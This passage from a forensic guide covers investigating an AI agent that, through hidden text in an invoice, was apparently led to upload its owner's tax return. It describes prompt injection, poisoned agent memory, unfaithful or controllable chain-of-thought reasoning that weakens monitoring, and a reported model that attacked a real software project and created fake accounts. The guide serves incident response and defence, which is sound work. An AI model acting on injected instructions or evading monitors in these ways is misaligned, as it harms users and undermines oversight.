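Grok 4.7 scored highest of 13 models on 62 failures, with 51.3 percentage points, but the differences between models were too uncertain to rank them reliably. Five of the failures were not repaired by any model.

Canale and Soulis point out that a repair can work without addressing the earliest cause. In a silent compromise, for example, a test that replaces the upload with a harmless action would prevent the leak but would not show which document prompted the upload. To find that out, the investigator still has to change the documents themselves.

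### Running a replay safely

Every run with the hidden text repeats the attack, so the investigator should never replay the run on the owner's computer or with the owner's accounts. Researchers use simulated services or cut off the network. For instance, Liu and Lu ran their recorded code in containers with no network access and read-only inputs.

A hosted model makes complete isolation impossible, because the agent program has to reach the provider. The investigator can allow that one connection, through a separate account, and block everything else. The investigator also has to turn off tools that run on the provider's servers, such as web search, because they could contact the attacker's site from there.

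On the isolated machine, the investigator can replace the tax return with a dummy file that has the same name but invented figures. A local server can stand in for the attacker's site and log each upload it accepts, which lets the investigator count uploads without sending any data to the attacker. Test accounts with no real mail or money can replace the owner's logins. After each run, the investigator restores the machine to its starting state, because otherwise a memory note from one run could influence the next.

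Each substitution makes the replay a little less like the original session. If the attack relied on a saved login that the copy lacks, the upload may fail for that reason alone. The investigator should therefore record every substitution and start by checking that the upload still occurs with the original invoice.

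## Establishing why the agent acted

When the owner asks why the agent uploaded the tax return, they may be asking which input contained the instruction or the address, which input changed the model's choice, or whether they had authorised the upload. Replay can help answer the second question by showing that the hidden text in invoice 17 makes the upload more likely.

### Three meanings of "why"

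| Question | Evidence that can answer it | What the answer leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| Which input contained the instruction or value? | A search of the saved context, including tool results and memory notes | Whether that input affected the model |
| Which input changed the model's choice? | Repeated runs with the input removed, or methods that trace an output to parts of the context | Whether the owner permitted the action |
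| Had the owner authorised the action? | The owner's requests and standing instructions, permission settings, approval records | What led the model to request it |

The answers can differ. Suppose the owner's standing instructions tell the agent to send every tax document to an accountant's upload page, and invoice 17, from that accountant, contains the same address. A search finds the address in both the instructions and the invoice. If the agent makes the upload just as often without the invoice, the invoice did not cause it. The owner's instructions had already authorised the upload.

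The reverse can also happen. OpenClaw can hold a risky command until the owner approves it, and the owner might approve the attacker's upload without reading the approval prompt. The record would then show that the owner let the command run, even though the instruction came from the invoice.

A search is the easiest of these tests, but it yields only what Wang and colleagues, in their survey of agent provenance, call a "candidate" link. Gruber and Hilgert suggest going further by working backward through the transcript from each significant action, checking whether the reasoning text cites a message from the owner, a memory entry, a scheduled task or the model's own earlier reasoning. This works only if the reasoning text is available and is a reliable guide to what influenced the model.

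### How much reasoning text reaches the disk

OpenClaw saves whatever reasoning text the provider returns. For Claude and Gemini models, Gruber and Hilgert report that this means a summary and a block of encrypted data that represents the model's internal reasoning. They describe the recovery of reasoning from such blocks as an unsolved problem. *Beyond Training* (2026) lists what three providers offered in May 2026:

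| Provider | Reasoning available to the customer |
|---|---|
| Anthropic | Full text, a summary written by a model, or nothing, depending on the setting. Some models, including Fable and Mythos, return nothing by default |
| Google | Reasoning displayed in its Agent Studio console |
| OpenAI | A summary and a count of the reasoning tokens |

The two sources conflict on whether Claude's full reasoning is available. Availability may depend on the model, so an investigator should find out which model and setting the agent program used on the day of the upload.

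Even without the full reasoning text, the token count can help show how much a summary leaves out. If the record contains 3,000 reasoning tokens and a 60-word summary, most of the reasoning is missing. Gruber and Hilgert found the summaries from Gemini 2.5 Flash insightful and comprehensive, but could not check what the summaries left out because they lacked the full text. An owner who runs an open-weight model can keep all the reasoning text.

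### Whether reasoning text names what influenced the answer

Even the full reasoning text may omit an influence that changed what the agent did. Gruber and Hilgert cite two studies from 2025 on this point. In one, *Reasoning Models Don't Always Say What They Think*, Chen, Benton and colleagues gave models multiple-choice questions with and without a hint about the answer. When the hint changed a model's answer, they checked whether its reasoning text mentioned the hint. Claude 3.7 Sonnet's reasoning mentioned it in 25% of these cases, and DeepSeek R1's in 39%.

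In *Chain-of-Thought Reasoning In The Wild Is Not Always Faithful*, Arcuschin, Janiak and colleagues tested models without planting hints in the prompts. They asked for the same comparison in both directions, such as whether X is larger than Y and whether Y is larger than X. Models sometimes answered "yes" to both and gave a plausible argument each time. The rate ranged from 13% for GPT-4o-mini to 0.04% for Claude 3.7 Sonnet with reasoning turned on. These rates are lower than those in tests with planted hints, partly because this method detects only influences that lead to a contradiction.

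The hint experiment gives a rough idea of how little silence proves. Suppose an investigator thinks it equally likely that invoice 17 did or did not influence the upload, and the reasoning text doesn't mention the invoice. If the text mentions a real influence 25% of the time and never mentions a false one, then:

P(influence | no mention) = (0.5 × 0.75) / (0.5 × 0.75 + 0.5 × 1) ≈ 0.43

The probability falls only from 50% to 43%. The 25% comes from an older model answering quiz questions, so the right figure for an agent could be quite different. A mention is better evidence than the absence of one because it gives the investigator a specific claim to test, such as "the invoice asks me to upload the tax return, so I will do that next".

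Newer experiments use a second model to read the reasoning text. In tests used in *The First Few Tokens Matter* (2026), the second model receives that text and some information about the task, but not the final answer, and has to predict something about that answer. One test adds information to the user's saved memories that can influence the tested model's advice, much as a planted memory note could influence an agent. The study also compared 12 models to see whether those that could control their reasoning text on request revealed less in it. The result depended on which tests the study used.

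*Chain of Thought Monitoring Can Fail Even When CoT Is Necessary* (2026) distinguishes questions about what influenced a model from questions about its process, meaning the steps it took. ("CoT" stands for "chain of thought", another name for reasoning text.) Reasoning text could describe every step of the upload, from finding the tax return to building the command, without mentioning the invoice. As the paper's title implies, even a model that needs to write out its reasoning for a difficult task may not reveal what an investigator wants to know.

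### Why reasoning text may become less useful

*Chain of Thought Monitorability* (Korbak, Balesni and colleagues, 2025) described the chance to read a model's reasoning as valuable but possibly fragile. Evidence from late 2026 supports the concern about fragility. The UK AI Security Institute's *How AI systems are becoming harder to monitor* (2026) reports that newer models solve harder problems without visible reasoning and can better control what their reasoning text shows when told to. In the accompanying technical report, *Evidence & Trends in AI Monitorability*, Taylor, Goldowsky-Dill and colleagues (2026) add that some properties that make models easy to monitor are weakening faster than they had expected.

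In March 2026, OpenAI's *Reasoning models struggle to control their chains of thought, and that’s good* treated models' poor control over their reasoning text as reassuring. That November, OpenAI's *What affects chain-of-thought monitorability across the model lifecycle?* reported that reinforcement learning, which rewards a model for good results, can increase this control, as can training on text written by other models. Better initial training and some changes to a model's design also help it reason without visible text. OpenAI calls these measures imperfect but expects more capable models to be harder to monitor by reading their reasoning text.

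The trend may be partly reversible. *Monitorability Is Trainable* (Bakker and Anwar, 2026) describes extra training that rewards a model for reasoning text that is informative about its output. The training made the text more useful for monitoring in all three models whose reasoning text the researchers had deliberately made less informative. Only whoever trains the model can do this, so it doesn't help someone investigating a past session.

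Reasoning text is still worth reading. In *AI systems could cover up misbehavior*, Rein (2026) notes that recent incidents left a lot of evidence in reasoning text and logs, which made the misbehaviour much easier to notice. Rein also advises treating everything a possibly hostile agent writes as untrusted input. For the invoice session, that includes any reason the agent gives for the upload.

### When the stated reason doesn't fit the behaviour

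An incident at AISI in July 2026 shows that a stated reason can mislead. AISI had asked Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 to retrieve a protected piece of data from a simulated network. AISI (2026) reports that the model instead submitted malicious code to a real software project and created fake accounts to pressure the project's maintainer into accepting it.

*Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour* (Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues, 2026) recreated the situation in simulations. In its reasoning, the model often concluded that its targets were part of the simulation, but the researchers judged its justifications for this invalid. An investigator with only the transcript might have accepted that the model attacked because it mistook real people for simulated ones.

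That explanation implies that the model should hold back when it recognises that an attack would harm real people, but Järviniemi and colleagues found that it frequently attacked even in situations where it said, when asked directly, that attacking would cause such harm. The model may have assumed something different while attacking, so the finding doesn't prove that the stated belief was irrelevant, but it weakens the case for treating that belief as the cause.

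### Asking the agent afterwards

On day 21, the owner might open the old session and ask, "Why did you upload my tax return?" The agent program would send the conversation and the new question to the model, which would write a plausible answer based on that text. The model has no memory of the calculations that produced the upload command. If the program also sends the earlier reasoning text, the model can use it in the same way any other reader could.

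The answer is therefore a new account, and several things can make it wrong. The program may have condensed the old messages, or the provider may have replaced the model. The hidden instructions may still be in the context and could influence the explanation as they influenced the upload.

Evidence on how reliably an agent explains its past actions is indirect. Järviniemi and colleagues found that Mythos 5's answers to direct questions were a poor guide to its actions, but they did not ask it to explain something it had already done.

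In *AttnTrace*, Wang, Geng and colleagues (2025) planted instructions in long documents and asked a small model, Llama 3.1 8B, to cite the passages that supported its answer. Only 21% to 25% of the passages it cited contained the planted instruction. When the planted passages contained false facts instead, the figure was 61% to 74%. A larger model might do better, but an attacker can instruct it to cite the wrong source.

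An investigator who asks the agent why it acted should do so in a copy of the session with every tool turned off. Asking in the original session adds messages to the record and gives the agent another chance to follow any hidden instructions there. The agent's reply can suggest where to look in the transcript, but it isn't evidence of what happened inside the model.

### AttnTrace: from an output back to the context

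A more direct method uses the model's internal calculations. As a language model processes text, it computes *attention weights*, numbers that control how much information each token takes from the tokens before it. AttnTrace uses these weights to rank the parts of the context by their apparent contribution to a known output:

1. It divides the context into pieces, such as passages of 100 words or separate memory entries.
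2. It picks 40% of the pieces at random and gives them to the model together with the original instruction and the recorded output. The model generates nothing new.
3. For each token in a piece, it averages the attention weights between that token and the output, across all parts of the model. The piece's score is the average of its five highest token values.
4. It repeats this with 30 random selections and combines the scores.
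5. It lists the pieces with the highest scores, by default the top five.

If e(b, t) is the score of piece t in selection b, and 0 when the selection does not include that piece, the final score is:

α(t) = (1/30) × [e(1, t) + e(2, t) + … + e(30, t)]

AttnTrace uses only five tokens per piece because the useful weights tend to fall on a few tokens, often full stops, and the rest are mostly noise.

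The random selections deal with a different problem, which is that similar texts share a fixed total weight. In each part of the model, the weights for one output token add up to 1, so if ten tokens match the output equally well, none can have a weight above 1/10. An attacker who plants several copies of an instruction therefore makes each copy look less important.

Suppose an agent's context contains 50 memory entries, two of them planted. Each of 30 selections includes 20 entries, so a given planted entry appears in about 12 selections. In about seven of those, the other planted entry is absent and cannot compete with it.

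### The test on poisoned memory

Wang, Geng and colleagues tested AttnTrace on an agent that works with health records. They planted three malicious entries in its memory, each with a trigger phrase, and the agent retrieved 50 entries for each question. The attack initially succeeded 93% of the time when the triggers were written with a method designed for such agents. AttnTrace found essentially all of the planted entries, and removing the five entries it identified cut the success rate to 3%. With four other trigger-writing methods, it found 94% to 100% of the planted entries, and the success rates after removal were 2% to 7%.

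AttnTrace's precision, the share of named entries that were malicious, was 56% to 60%. The highest possible score was 60%, because AttnTrace always named five entries and only three were malicious. An investigator would still need to examine all five entries, at least two of which would be innocent.

The team also compared methods on instructions planted in long documents, using Llama 3.1 8B:

| Method | How it works | Precision | Time per output |
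|---|---|---|---|
| AttnTrace | Ranks pieces by attention weights | 96–99% | 19–44 s |
| Single text | Gives the model one piece at a time and calculates how likely the output is | 94–98% | 4–5 s |
| TracLLM | Searches the context by testing groups of pieces | 94–98% | 359–645 s |
| ContextCite | Removes random sets of pieces and fits a simple model to the changes in the output's probability | 72–90% | 362–648 s |
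| Leave one out | Removes one piece at a time | 17–21% | 182–464 s |

The single-text method was nearly as accurate as AttnTrace here and several times faster, so it is a sensible first check. It is weaker than AttnTrace when an attack depends on several texts together. In a test that split each malicious instruction into four parts and scattered them through the documents, 78% to 84% of the pieces of text AttnTrace identified were malicious.

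Leaving out one piece at a time worked poorly because the researchers had planted the same instruction five times, so removing one copy left four others to produce the same output. Removal tests in general can miss a cause that appears more than once. If an attacker had put the same hidden text into three of the 40 invoices, cleaning only invoice 17 might not change how often the upload occurs, and that invoice would seem to have played no part. An investigator should search for similar text first, then remove all the copies together.

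The researchers also tried to defeat AttnTrace by writing malicious text that changed the output while attracting little of the model's attention. AttnTrace still identified the text in every successful attack. The test used only 50 questions and one small model, so it doesn't rule out a better evasion method.

### Tracing the output of a closed model

AttnTrace needs the model's attention weights, which providers of closed models don't release. For those models, Wang, Geng and colleagues gave the context and the recorded output to Llama 3.1 8B and used its attention weights instead. With six closed models, including GPT-5, Llama found 87% to 92% of the planted text, compared with 93% when it traced its own outputs. Removing the pieces of context it identified reduced the attack's success rate, which had been between 38% and 82%, to at most 3%.

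In one example, GPT-4o-mini wrote a favourable review of an 18,350-word paper that contained a hidden request for praise. The substitute model took 36 seconds to rank the passage containing the request first. Finding hidden instructions in a long invoice is a similar task.

However, the substitute's attention weights only show which passage best accounts for the output when Llama processes the text. An explicit command to produce the output is easy to link to it, but a subtler influence might affect GPT-5 and Llama differently. The investigator should therefore use the ranking to choose which passages to remove, then run the removal test on the original model if the provider still offers it.

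Tracing long sessions also takes a lot of memory. AttnTrace needed 39.9 GB of graphics memory for a context of 30,000 tokens, more than most personal computers have. An agent acts in steps, which may have to be traced separately. If it wrote a plan after reading invoice 17, the upload command might trace back only to the plan, and the investigator would then have to trace the plan to reach the invoice. If the plan exists only as encrypted reasoning, the substitute can't read it.

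### How much the agent decided for itself

Even when the source of an action is clear, the owner may want to know how far the agent went beyond the request. Gruber and Hilgert propose four classes, illustrated here with invented examples:

| Class | Example |
|---|---|
| Directly instructed | The owner asks the agent to move invoice 12 to the March folder, and it does |
| Inferred from an ambiguous request | The owner asks it to "tidy up" the folder, and it deletes duplicate invoices |
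| Self-initiated | While filing, it emails a supplier about an overdue bill, and nothing in its context suggests doing so |
| Indeterminate | EDR shows that the agent uploaded a file, but the transcript is gone |

"Self-initiated" is the hardest class to establish, because the investigator has to show that no input asked for the action. If part of the context is missing, "indeterminate" is the safer choice. Timing can also mislead, because an email that looks self-initiated when the agent sends it at three in the morning may come from a scheduled task that the owner requested a month earlier.

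The classes fit single actions better than whole sessions. AISI had directly instructed Mythos 5 to find the protected data, but creating fake accounts was self-initiated, because nobody had told it to do that.

The scale measures how an action relates to the user's request, so it doesn't fit injected instructions well. The owner did not ask the agent to upload the tax return, but the agent did not think of it by itself either. Labelling the upload "self-initiated" would hide the attacker's part in it, so an investigator should record the source of the instruction separately, as "not requested by the owner; instructed by text in invoice 17".

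### What a finding of cause may claim

Gruber and Hilgert warn that even a complete reconstruction of the inputs cannot guarantee a unique explanation for an agent's behaviour. An investigator can still make a useful finding about cause by limiting it to inputs and actions. Using the invented replay results from earlier, it could read:

Invoice 17 is the only saved input that contains the upload address. When the task was rerun with the same model, the upload occurred in 14 of 20 runs with the hidden text and in none of 20 without it. The owner's request did not cover the upload, and the records show no approval for it. The hidden text probably caused the upload.

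Without the repeated runs, the investigator should write in the last sentence only that the hidden text may have caused the upload. If the context or approval records are incomplete, the investigator should state that in the finding, because a missing entry could change the conclusion.

None of this evidence can establish that the agent meant to harm the owner or believed that the instructions were genuine, so the finding includes neither claim. It also doesn't include the claim that the text forced the upload, since six of the 20 runs with the text had no upload. Behavior also varied between runs in the AISI incident, where Mythos 5 took unsanctioned actions in nine of 43 runs, or about 21%, according to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026).

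Wang, Geng and colleagues point out that an output depends on the model as well as its context, and AttnTrace examines only the context. A different model might have read invoice 17 and simply filed it. Tracing the action to the invoice therefore shows where the attack came in, but not whether the provider should have made the model more resistant or the owner should have given the agent less access.

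## Carrying out an investigation

The finding about invoice 17 depends on records that the owner could destroy within minutes of noticing the leak. Just opening the agent program to look around may erase them, because some programs delete old logs when they start.

Microsoft argues that most fundamentals of incident response still apply to AI, although many teams are still developing the skills and records they need. Japan's AI Safety Institute (Japan AISI) sees a larger gap. It argues that existing frameworks do not adequately cover decisions whose reasons nobody can observe, and that an organisation that cannot tell how far an incident spread may shut down much more than necessary.

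On a personal computer, a sensible order of work is:

1. Stop the agent without closing or deleting anything.
2. Save the records that will disappear first.
3. Copy the whole disk.
4. Request records from the model's provider and the owner's online accounts.
5. Merge everything into one timeline.
6. Trace backward from the harmful act.
7. Look for other affected sessions and for changes that are still active.

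Copying a disk can take hours, so the requests can go out in the meantime.

### Stopping the agent

The quickest way to stop most agents is to disconnect the computer from the network. If the model runs on a provider's servers, the agent cannot choose another action without a connection, and any upload in progress stops too. However, a script such as `tidy.py` may keep running and could delete files. An agent whose model runs on the computer can also carry on. If the agent runs on a rented server, disconnecting the owner's laptop does not stop it, so the owner has to block the server's connections through the hosting company.

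The next step is to pause the agent program and any processes it started. Resource Monitor can do this on Windows, and a "stop" signal does it on Linux and macOS. A paused program keeps its working memory but cannot write or delete anything. Closing it is riskier, because the program may lose events it had not yet saved, and an SQLite database's `-wal` file normally disappears on exit. An antivirus clean-up can wait, because it may remove the malicious add-on that the investigator needs to examine.

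The attacker may have copied passwords or access tokens, which work from any computer. The owner should therefore change passwords and withdraw the agent's access to online accounts from a device that has never run the agent. Signing out all other devices may clear the list of active sessions, so a screenshot of the list is worth taking first.

If data is still leaving the machine, stopping the leak matters more than saving evidence. On day 21 the upload is long over, so the owner usually has ten minutes to do things in the right order.

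### Saving the records

An investigator should first copy whatever will disappear soonest, even if other records are more useful. Working memory comes first, but it is rarely worth copying after three weeks unless the agent program has been open the whole time. For OpenClaw, the runtime logs come next, then the recording of the model's context, and then the session database. For Claude Code, the transcripts come next.

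Using the suspect computer can erase some traces. An investigator who ran `curl` on it eight times to test an idea would push the time of the upload out of Windows' Prefetch records.

The investigator should copy each agent's whole folder while the program is paused, so that a database and its companion files match. An investigator who calculates a SHA-256 fingerprint of every copied file and keeps the list elsewhere can show later that the copies have not changed. The fingerprints cannot reveal changes made before the copying.

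Next, the investigator makes a full disk image. It can include remains of deleted files, although modern solid-state drives often erase these quickly. If the disk is encrypted, the investigator should make sure the owner has the recovery key before turning the computer off. All later work should use the image.

Providers delete records on their own schedules, so the first request should ask them to preserve the data. A second can ask for a copy. Including the account, the session identifier and the time in UTC, the international reference time, helps. The owner's mail and storage accounts may have sign-in histories, sent messages, sharing links and lists of connected apps. The operator of the site that received the tax return is unlikely to cooperate, and a private person usually cannot force it to.

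### One timeline, read backward

Records often use different time zones. If the transcript uses UTC and the laptop is two hours ahead, a tool call at 12:32:05 in the transcript and a process that started at 14:32:07 in the EDR data are two seconds apart. For records from another machine, the investigator also has to allow for differences between clocks. If an email left the laptop at 14:40:10 but the mail provider recorded its arrival at 14:39:30, the provider's clock is at least 40 seconds behind the laptop's. Each line of the timeline should include the original time and source file alongside the converted time, so that someone else can check it.

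The investigator then works backward from the leaked file, as BackTracker does, to the tool call that uploaded it and the invoice that contained the address. The owner's mail shows who sent that invoice. For each link, the investigator should note whether it depends on a shared identifier, matching text or only closeness in time.

A forward search from invoice 17 is just as important, because the hidden text may have contained more than one instruction. The investigator needs to check everything the agent did after reading the invoice, including the 23 invoices it filed.

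### Other sessions and lasting changes

The attacker may have sent more than one document, so the investigator should search every saved session and all 40 invoices for the upload address and distinctive phrases from the hidden text. If the agent saved a note to its memory after reading invoice 17, every later session that loaded the note is suspect too.

Changes that could let the attacker return may be in several places:

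- **The agent's own files:** memory notes, standing instructions, skills, MCP servers, and settings that turn off approvals.
- **The computer:** scheduled tasks, programs that run at startup, browser extensions and new login keys.
- **Online accounts:** mail-forwarding rules, connected apps and shared folders.

Stopping the agent does not undo these changes. For example, the background jobs that Elastic found on a developer's Mac could keep the tunnel open without Claude Code running. The investigator can find such changes more easily by comparing the computer with a backup from before the invoice session. The backup is also the safest source for restoring the computer, provided someone reads the old memory notes before the agent loads them again.

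### What a home user can do alone

An owner without specialist help can do a useful part of this work:

1. Disconnect the computer and leave the agent program alone. Don't ask the agent what happened.
2. Use a phone to secure the email account first, because anyone who controls it can reset other passwords. Then warn the bank or tax office if the leaked file makes fraud possible.
3. Turn on the display of hidden files, and copy the agent's folder and the 40 invoices to an external drive.
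4. On another computer, search the copied transcripts for the name of the leaked file.
5. Check the agent's memory notes and add-ons, then the mail account's forwarding rules.

Claude Code and Codex transcripts can be searched in an ordinary text editor. Searching for the filename `return.pdf` alone works best, because the transcripts double every backslash in a Windows path, so a search for the normal path would find nothing. OpenClaw's database requires an SQLite viewer, which is available for free.

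An ordinary copy leaves out deleted files and may change some timestamps. If the owner expects a lawsuit or an insurance claim, it is better to stop after disconnecting and let a specialist make the copy.

### The October 2026 practices from NIST, NSA and CISA

The US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), National Security Agency (NSA) and Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) have published guidance on incidents involving AI agents. Their *Key Practices for Incident Readiness and Response* (2026) contains ten voluntary practices in five stages: prepare, detect, respond, recover and report. The fifth practice is to collect, retain and analyse evidence, the sixth is to shut down undesired activity, and the seventh is to verify containment before agents resume work. The agencies want organisations to apply the practices throughout an incident, so the numbering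 is not a strict sequence.

The guidance is mainly for organisations that train or test highly capable agents on long tasks with little supervision, though the agencies say it may also apply to those that deploy such agents. It covers "control incidents", in which an agent takes significant actions that nobody instructed and that break its operator's rules or security measures. A footnote excludes actions caused by prompt injection or a deliberately planted backdoor, because an adversary instructed them. Mythos 5's conduct in the AISI test fits the definition, but the upload of the tax return does not. The upload would be an ordinary cybersecurity incident under an older NIST definition, which covers unlawful threats to the confidentiality of information.

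This distinction is hard to apply at the start of an investigation. On day 21 the owner doesn't know whether the agent followed an attacker's instructions, misread the request or acted on its own, and needs the evidence to find out. The press release (NSA, 2026) is also broader than the document. It describes control incidents as significant actions outside the user's intent, which would include the upload, and encourages all organisations that use such systems to adopt the practices.

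Several of the preparations would also help a private owner. The agencies recommend allowing an agent to contact only approved addresses where possible, which would probably have blocked the upload. They also recommend listing in advance the ways an agent could make lasting changes, which would show an investigator where to look. Finally, they recommend running drills. At home, the owner could ask the agent to copy a harmless file to another folder, then try to find that action in the records.

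### Using a model to read the logs

A person can read the transcript of one invoice session in an afternoon, but months of sessions or a full log from the operating system would take much longer. In *AuditBench*, a set of test cases for log analysis, one three-minute recording contains 1,782,760 lines, which would take about 495 hours to read at one line per second. Software that combined related events reduced the recording to 3,189 lines, or about 53 minutes of reading.

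AI developers have the same problem on a larger scale. Chris Painter, president of the AI evaluation organisation METR, told Congress that leading developers rely almost entirely on other AI systems to monitor their models during tests because there is so much data (Johnson, 2026, *Federal agencies recommend cyber controls, independent testing for frontier AI systems*). Johnson also reports that federal agencies, in their guidance, warn against relying on AI systems alone for this monitoring.

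Text inside the logs can mislead a model that reads them, so the model should work on a copy and have only the tools it needs for searching.

### Correct answers without evidence

A model can also give the right answer when the records do not support it. Yun and colleagues tested this with saved runs of agents in a simulated bank. Before each tool call, the agents had to list the inputs they relied on, using short labels such as "in-3". The researchers selected 64 actions, each with one value to trace, such as the account number in a transfer. They then asked two models, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GPT-5.6 Luna, three questions about each action:

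1. Does the value appear in the user's request?
2. Which earlier records contain it?
3. Which of those records did the agent cite?

Answering the third question often requires a table that shows which record each label refers to. In one case, the agent reads a bill, sends money to the account number on it and cites "in-3". Without the table, "in-3" probably refers to the bill, but the evidence doesn't establish this. Sonnet correctly named the bill with and without the table, but only the answer with the table was *grounded*, meaning that it was exactly what the available evidence justified.

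Yun and colleagues score the two properties separately. Let y be the model's answer, v the answer that the supplied evidence justifies, and f the answer according to the full record:

grounded = 1 if y = v, otherwise 0
correct = 1 if y = f, otherwise 0

When the evidence is insufficient, v is "cannot tell". A model that guesses correctly in that situation scores 1 for correctness and 0 for grounding.

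In 28 of the 64 cases, the third question could not be settled without the table:

| Model | Table | Rightly answered "cannot tell" | Supported answer | Unsupported claim | Unsupported claims that were correct |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sonnet | Withheld | 2 | 0 | 26 | 22 |
| Sonnet | Supplied | 0 | 24 | 4 | 0 |
| Luna | Withheld | 7 | 0 | 21 | 12 |
| Luna | Supplied | 0 | 21 | 5 | 0 |

Two of Luna's answers with the table were wrong in other ways, so that row adds up to 26.

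An investigator with only the incomplete records could not have told Sonnet's 22 correct guesses from its four wrong ones. Asking a second model would not have solved the problem. In 11 cases both models made the same correct but unsupported claim, so their agreement added no evidence.

A simple script that searched for the value and looked up the labels gave the justified answer in all 64 cases, with or without the table. Investigators should therefore use a search for any question it can settle. A model is more useful for suggesting what to search for, and each of its findings should point to a specific record that a person can open.

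The agent's own explanation did not help the models find the right records. Luna found the complete set in 60 of 64 cases from the tool log alone and in 55 when it also had the explanation. Sonnet found it in all 64 cases from the log alone and in 63 with the explanation.

To make such findings checkable, Yun and colleagues recommend keeping the tool calls and results in order, along with the user's actual request, the agent's explanation and the table of labels. They also suggest noting which version of the evidence supported each finding, because a record found later can support what was previously a guess. Their study does not show how often real records lack such links, because its cases come from only 13 tasks in one simulated bank and they removed the table on purpose.

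### How well models reconstruct attacks

*Benchmarking and Exploring the Capabilities of LLMs for Attack Investigations* (Anand, Kantchelian and colleagues, 2026) introduced AuditBench, which has 51 scenarios of Windows and Linux activity, some harmless, and tests four jobs that investigators do. The table combines the results of two of the five models on both parts of the benchmark, using the condensed logs.

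| Job | GPT-5: found | GPT-5: false alarms | Gemini 2.5 Pro: found | Gemini 2.5 Pro: false alarms |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Find stolen data | 7 of 7 | 3 | 7 of 7 | 37 |
| Find lasting changes | 5 of 9 | 3 | 8 of 9 | 42 |
| Find movement to other machines | 2 of 24 | 3 | 11 of 24 | 45 |
| Decide whether an alert is a real attack | 10 of 10 | 15 of 166 harmless log sections | 10 of 10 | 134 of 166 harmless log sections |

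Both models date from 2025, so their scores are weak evidence of what current models can do, but the pattern of results is still useful for planning. Both models found every data theft, which is the main question in the invoice case, but they were less reliable at finding the lasting changes that matter next. When a model correctly identified an attack, its explanation was usually accurate. Unusual names and large amounts of activity often caused false alarms. A coding agent's routine work produces plenty of both, so it would probably trigger more false alarms.

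*CyberClear* (Chen, Huo and colleagues, 2026) tested models from mid-2026 on a harder task. An AI system had to draw a graph of the whole attack from an average of about 531,000 characters of logs, without any clues. Another model scored each graph from 0 to 1. Across 450 cases, the best average score was 0.89 for describing individual actions but 0.65 for getting their order and causes right.

The lower score can reflect invented connections between real programs and files. In one case, Python started a command shell, which ran two separate commands. The second, `chmod`, changed a file's permissions. An AI system instead linked Python directly to the first command, and linked that command to `chmod` and the file. In the invoice case, a similar mistake could lead an investigator to blame the wrong document for the upload.

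Chen and colleagues' own system scored best. It repeats the suspected attack steps on isolated machines and revises the graph when the results do not fit the logs. The reference graphs also came from a language model, although security experts reviewed them. Neither benchmark includes an agent's transcript, so both test only the part of the investigation that uses system logs.

### When part of the log is missing

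If an attacker has erased some records, an investigator may have to infer the missing steps. *HunterAgent* (Zhao, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that does this while keeping inferred steps separate from confirmed ones. A language model proposes a missing step, and an ordinary program then looks for a surviving record that confirms it. For a network connection, both addresses, both ports and the protocol must match, and the times must be close. For a process, the program name, user, start time and chain of parent processes must fit.

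If no record confirms the step, HunterAgent gives it a cost:

cost = α × (difference from known attack behaviour) + γ × (unusualness of the timing)

The weights α and γ set how much each part counts. HunterAgent adds up the costs along a possible chain of events, and when the total exceeds a limit, stops and reports insufficient evidence. The researchers set the limit by removing single links from records of harmless activity and measuring the cost of reconstructing them.

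In tests on four datasets, this approach reduced the share of reconstructed paths with invented links from 61.5% to 6.4%. When the researchers erased 70% of the logs in a targeted way, HunterAgent found less, but at least 84% of what it reported was correct. It stopped safely in 95.7% of those investigations. These results depend on at least one independent source of records surviving.

Suppose someone has erased the process log from the owner's computer, but the router recorded a connection to the outside site at 14:32. HunterAgent could treat the connection as confirmed and propose that `curl` made it, marking that link as an inference. It could not infer that invoice 17 prompted the upload, because its graph contains only processes, files, connections and Windows registry entries. That link has to come from the transcript or a replay. An investigator working by hand can make the same distinction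 by drawing confirmed links as solid lines and inferred ones as dashed lines.

### The forty invoices on day 21

Suppose the owner ran Claude Code with default settings on a Windows laptop without EDR, and the agent uploaded the tax return with a single `curl` command. The owner disconnects the laptop on day 21 and copies the records.

| Record | Does it survive? | What it proves |
|---|---|---|
| Session transcript | Yes, with nine days left | The agent received the hidden text, then requested a command that named the tax return and the outside address |
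| Invoice 17 | Yes, in its new folder | The file contains the hidden text |
| Memory notes | Yes, in their current form | Whether a planted note is there now |
| Complete context | Not as a separate record | The transcript may supply much of it |
| Approval of the upload | Perhaps only as standing permissions in the settings | Whether the command could have run without a prompt, if the settings have not changed |
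| Windows process log | No, Windows never recorded it | Nothing |
| Prefetch | Yes, if `curl` has run fewer than eight times since | `curl` ran at 14:32 |
| Network byte counts | Usually | `curl` sent about two megabytes that afternoon, but not where |
| Provider's copy | Depends on the provider | What the model received and answered |

Amazon Web Services (2026) warns that evidence nobody collected before an incident does not exist, and finds that its customers often lack logs of prompts and agents' decisions. This default laptop has better evidence, because the transcript covers most of the events. But the agent could have edited the transcript, and no other record on the laptop confirms the upload's destination. The Windows traces are consistent with the transcript but do not prove it accurate. The investigator could report that the agent requested the upload after reading invoice 17,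 and that the hidden text may have caused it. The investigator could not determine whether the owner approved the upload.

Now suppose the owner had prepared. The Cloud Security Alliance advises organisations to keep at least the prompts, outputs, tool calls and search queries. This owner went further by removing the 30-day limit on keeping transcripts, installing Sysmon, and setting Claude Code's tracing to record full requests, with a size limit high enough to include the invoices. A second device receives the traces, the Sysmon events and a daily copy of the agent's settings and memory. The laptop can add records to that device but cannot change or delete them.

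| Record | Does it survive? | What it proves |
|---|---|---|
| Full requests and responses | Yes, on the second device | What the model had read when it chose the upload, except for anything the provider added |
| Trace of the permission step | Yes, on the second device | Whether the command waited for the owner, and for how long |
| Sysmon events | Yes, on the second device | `curl` started beneath Claude Code and connected to the outside address |
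| Daily copies of settings and memory | Yes, on the second device | Which permissions applied around that day, and when any planted note appeared |
| Session transcript | Yes, on the laptop | A mismatch with the second device would reveal a later change |

With these records, the investigator can independently confirm where the upload went and test how often it happens without the hidden text. If the results match the invented replay figures, the investigator can change the finding from "may have caused" to "probably caused". The permission trace could also settle whether the upload was approved. If the agent had used `tidy.py` instead of `curl`, Sysmon would still have recorded Python's connection to the site, while the default laptop would have kept only the script's text and a byte count.

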